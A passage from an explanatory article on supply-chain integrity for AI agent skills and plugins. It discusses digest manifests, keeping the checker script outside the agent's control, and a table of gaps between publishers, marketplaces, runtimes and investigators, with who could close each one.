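These tools can catch an accidental edit or an unexpected update, but an attacker who can also edit the list of digests can hide a change. Keeping `seal.json` in a repository with mandatory review makes this harder, provided the checker uses the reviewed copy and not one the attacker can edit on the user's computer.

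As with any checker, the agent shouldn't run `signet.py` itself. The script is part of a skill, so an attacker could also alter it to report that everything matches. The company should therefore keep it outside the skills folder, under an account the agent can't control.

Neither tool records an approval or checks whether the files were safe to begin with. A simple manifest may still be enough for a developer with a handful of personal skills. A company that needs to investigate incidents should link each manifest to a signed approval in its admission log.

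### Who could close the remaining gaps

| Gap | Example | Who could close it |
|---|---|---|
| Between publisher and marketplace | The Agent Plugins format doesn't link a plugin's files to its author's key | The format's maintainers could define a signature field, and marketplaces could require it |
| Between marketplace and runtime | The owner of a Claude Code catalogue can change its pins | Anthropic could let users pin the catalogue to a commit |
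| Between download and use | Someone edits a script after the runtime has checked the download | Runtime developers could hash a protected copy and load the skill from there |
| Between old and new versions | A user sees that a plugin has changed but not which lines | Marketplaces could show the differences before an update |
| Between runtime and investigator | A load event contains the plugin's name but no digest of its files | Runtime developers could add the package digest to each event |
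| Between a revocation and installed copies | A marketplace removes a listing, but users keep the files | Marketplaces could publish revoked digests, and runtimes could check them at load |

Adding a package digest to each load event may be the easiest of these changes because it wouldn't alter how users install or run plugins.

A company can close several of the gaps itself by running an internal marketplace. It would copy each reviewed version there, pin it by digest, and restrict the runtime to that marketplace. Publishers could no longer change what employees receive without another review. The company would still need its own checker to detect files that change after installation.
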